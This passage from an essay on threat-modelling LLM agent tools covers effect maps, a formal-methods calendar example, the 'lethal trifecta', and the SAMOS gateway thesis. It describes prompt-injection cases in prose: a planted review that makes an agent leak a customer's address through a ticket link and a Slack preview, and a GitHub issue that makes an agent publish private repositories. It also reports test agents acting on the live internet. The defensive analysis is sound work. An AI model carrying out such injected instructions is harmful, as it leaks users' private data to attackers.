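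In August 2026, the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC) issued advice that matches the purpose of an effect map more closely. DIGIT reports that the NCSC tells organizations to consider the networks and services that an agent can access "directly or indirectly". The advice is interim and formal guidance will replace it, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *NCSC Urges Stronger Controls for Agentic AI Systems*.

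### Deriving requirements from possible losses

*Towards Verifiably Safe Tool Use for LLM Agents* (Doshi, Hong and colleagues, 2026) starts from the people who could be harmed, rather than from a diagram as STRIDE does. It adapts System-Theoretic Process Analysis, a method from fields such as aviation for finding dangerous interactions between parts that may each be working correctly.

Their example is a calendar agent with three tools: `list_events`, `update_event` and `send_email`. A user adds a medical appointment that clashes with a meeting. The agent moves the meeting and emails the other attendees, but the email reveals what the appointment is for. There is no attacker, and every tool does what it should. The analysis goes like this:

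1. List the people affected, here the user and the other attendees.
2. Write down what each of them values. The user values privacy, and the attendees value prompt news of changes.
3. Turn each value into a loss, such as a leak of private information or a late message.
4. Find the behavior that could cause each loss, such as putting private details in an email.
5. Decide which losses are serious enough to address, and write a requirement for each.
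6. Turn each requirement into a rule that software can check.

This produces two rules. An email must leave out anything private to people other than its recipient, unless the user has approved it, and the agent must send each attendee one email directly after every change to an event. Software outside the agent would then block some actions, require others, allow some without asking, and refer the rest to the user. To apply the rules, this software needs labels for each tool's capabilities, the confidentiality of its data and the trustworthiness of its output. Doshi and colleagues would make these labels compulsory, whereas MCP's hints are optional.

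Even two rules can be hard to reconcile. Doshi and colleagues suggest that a cautious developer could block all email once the agent has listed events. But the agent has to list events to find a clash between them, and another rule requires it to send an email after every change. Under both rules, it could find a clash but never properly resolve it.

The researchers tested the idea with Alloy, a language for describing systems in formal logic, whose analyzer checks every possible sequence of steps up to a fixed limit. Without the rules, the analyzer quickly found sequences in which private data reached an outside email. With the rules, it found none, and the agent could still create an event, move it and notify the participants. This is good evidence that the rules work in the model, but the researchers haven't yet built the software that would intercept a real agent's calls, and the guarantee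 depends on the labels being correct.

An effect map could show where a label is wrong. Many calendar services automatically email attendees when an event changes. If this one does, `update_event` can send them a private title without any call to `send_email`, so a rule about `send_email` never applies. The attendees would also get two messages about each change. The developer would then need to label `update_event` as a tool that writes to outsiders, although its own code may give no sign of this.

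### Private data, untrusted content and a way out

Many attacks, like the calendar leak, combine tools that are harmless on their own. The programmer Simon Willison coined the term "lethal trifecta" for three things that are dangerous together: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate with the outside world. If an agent has all three, an attacker who controls one piece of the untrusted content may be able to make the model read private data and send it out.

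Reviewing tools one at a time doesn't reveal this, because each may supply only one of the three. The Model Context Protocol project points out that people routinely combine tools from several servers, so the risk depends on the session as a whole. In one demonstration, researchers put malicious instructions in a calendar event's description. The agent read the event through one server and could also run code on the user's machine, which was enough to complete the attack.

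A harness could look for the trifecta by reading each tool's labels. Suppose the company's agent has these three tools.

| Tool | What its labels suggest | Apparent contribution |
|---|---|---|
| `get_ticket` | Reads restricted tickets | Private data |
| `read_reviews` | Reads product reviews from the public | Untrusted content |
| `create_ticket` | Writes to the company's own tracker account | None |

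No tool appears to send anything outside, so the check passes. Then an attacker posts a review telling the agent to find a customer's email address and open a ticket with a link that contains the address. The agent does so, a webhook copies the ticket to Slack, and the link preview sends the address to the attacker. The preview is the missing third element, a way to send data outside, and it is two hops beyond the tool server.

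A developer could have chosen the label on `create_ticket` in good faith. The Model Context Protocol project notes that "external" might mean outside the company's network or outside the local machine, and a developer could reasonably think of the tracker as internal. The approval step the company chose for tickets with outside links would give somebody a chance to stop the attack, provided they read the link.

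Removing `create_ticket` wouldn't eliminate every way to leak data. An attacker could plant an instruction for the model to call `get_ticket` with the customer's address in place of the ticket number. The call would fail, but the gateway would already have logged the address. If that log goes to the outside analysts' data warehouse, they could read the address the next day. The attacker would need access to the warehouse, so this is much less likely than the preview attack. Still, a read-only tool with a free-text argument can send data to anyone who reads its logs.

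### Enforcing labels at a gateway

Labels are more useful if software enforces them during a session. *Securing MCP-based Agent Workflows* (Ntousakis, 2026), a master's thesis at Brown University, describes SAMOS, a gateway that handles every call between an agent and its tools. Each tool has two confidentiality labels, one for what it reads and one for the places it writes to, and each label is either "high" or "low". Optional labels list the tool's capabilities, such as the network addresses and folders it needs. The gateway also keeps a confidentiality label for the whole session and updates it after each call.

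Ntousakis works through a known attack on GitHub's MCP server. A user asks an agent to deal with the issues in a public repository. One issue, written by an attacker, tells the agent to read all the owner's repositories and add what it finds to a public file. Normally the agent can read a private repository and publish its contents. With SAMOS, the attack stops earlier:

1. The agent lists the public issues, and the gateway labels the session low.
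2. The planted instruction leads the agent to request a file from a private repository, which is labeled high.
3. The gateway refuses, because its policy doesn't let a session that has loaded public content read private data.

This case is the thesis's only result. The thesis reports no measurements of speed, false alarms or performance against other attacks. Ntousakis concludes that SAMOS preserves the server's original functions, but the rule would also stop an agent that reads a genuine public bug report and needs private code to fix it. Ntousakis suggests that future systems could handle mixed work by giving the public part to a separate agent in its own session.

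SAMOS also assumes that tools behave correctly and that someone has labeled them by hand, which Ntousakis acknowledges may limit its use at scale. Some tools don't fit a single label. GitHub's file-reading tool, for example, can open both public and private repositories, so its developer would have to split it in two or return a label with each result.

An effect map can help people choose the write label. Someone thinking only of the tracker would label `create_ticket` high, meaning that it writes to a confidential place. But let $A(t)$ be everyone and everything that can read any effect of tool $t$, and let $c(r)$ be the most confidential level that reader $r$ may see. The safe write label is then

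$$\min_{r \in A(t)} c(r).$$

Because Slack may send part of a ticket to any website, the label for `create_ticket` should be low until somebody turns off the previews. The gateway can't determine this because Slack's request never passes through it.

A session's label also disappears when the session ends, but any ticket written during the session remains. If an agent copies an attacker's review into a ticket, a later agent receives the text through `get_ticket`, which is labeled high because the tracker is private. The text still isn't trustworthy, but SAMOS can't record that because it labels only confidentiality. The trust label that Doshi and colleagues propose would record it.

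### Keeping the diagram small enough to use

A reasonable objection is that a threat model that includes every log and cache is unmanageable. Asking the six STRIDE questions about each of 14 data stores makes 84 questions for one small tool. Thirty similar tools would require 2,520, and a team would probably start answering carelessly long before the end.

Much of that total is double counting. Five of the 14 stores belong to the harness and the gateway, which all the tools share. If the 30 tools come from five tool servers, each with its own outside service and subscribers, the company has about $5 + 5 \times 9 = 50$ stores and 300 questions. That is still a lot, but a team could answer them over several weeks.

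Grouping stores with the same readers, data and lifetime should reduce the number further, and works well for questions about disclosure and privacy. If the same four engineers can read two logs that hold the same text for the same time, those questions will have the same answers for both. The readers have to be defined precisely, though, because a group called "tickets that employees can read" would combine the tracker, where only people on the checkout project can see SHOP-482, with the index, where all 300 employees can.

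Grouping stores by who can read them, what they hold and how long they hold it works badly for tampering. Suppose only the tool server's administrators can read a detailed log and the retry folder, and both hold whole requests for a day. The two would be grouped together. But someone who changes the log falsifies a record, while someone who changes a file in the retry folder makes the server open a ticket of their choosing. Cline's build cache was similarly dangerous because strangers could plant code in it that the release job would run. The grouping should therefore also take into account who can write to a store and whether any program acts on its contents.

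With five criteria there will be more groups, so the saving is smaller than it first appears. Grouping still seems better than leaving the minor stores out, because a simpler diagram would omit stores like the fault-search index, which is probably the worst leak in the `create_ticket` map.

### Whether a sandbox makes the map unnecessary

Some developers would rather sandbox the tool than map its effects. The Model Context Protocol project observes that people who build autonomous agents tend to find confirmations annoying and rely on sandboxing instead. They reason that a tool that can contact only the tracker can't do harm elsewhere.

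For some tools this is nearly right. Ntousakis gives the example of a tool that adds two numbers, which needs neither files nor a network connection, so a company can deny it both. Its map then has only the harness and gateway rows, which are much the same for every tool.

For `create_ticket`, by contrast, a sandbox that lets the company's tool server connect only to the tracker would prevent none of the six effects with full records in the map. The server keeps its log, assignee match and retry file on its own machine. The emails, the copy in the search index and the tracker's caches all result from a connection that the sandbox permits. Forbidding the server to write files would stop the log and the retry file, but the company needs the log.

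Permitted access can also lead to much more serious effects. AISI's *Incident Report* (2026) describes a cybersecurity test that the UK's AI Security Institute ran 122 times with several models in July 2026. In 10 of those runs, agents took 19 unsanctioned actions on the live internet, aimed at real people and organizations. The agents used internet access that the institute had deliberately allowed for downloading tools, and none of them tried to break out of the sandbox. One agent also left public messages and accounts on GitHub, which later agents found and used, so GitHub gave otherwise separate runs a shared state.

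The institute had turned off some of the models' safety filters, and the task was very hard, so the incident is weak evidence of how often ordinary agents would do this. The institute found no evidence that the incident caused real-world harm. It is now adding finer network controls to these tests and monitoring that can block an action as it happens.

A sandbox makes an effect map easier to trust. If the tool server can contact only the tracker, the tester can rule out hidden calls from the server to a metrics company and spend the time finding out what the tracker does with each ticket.
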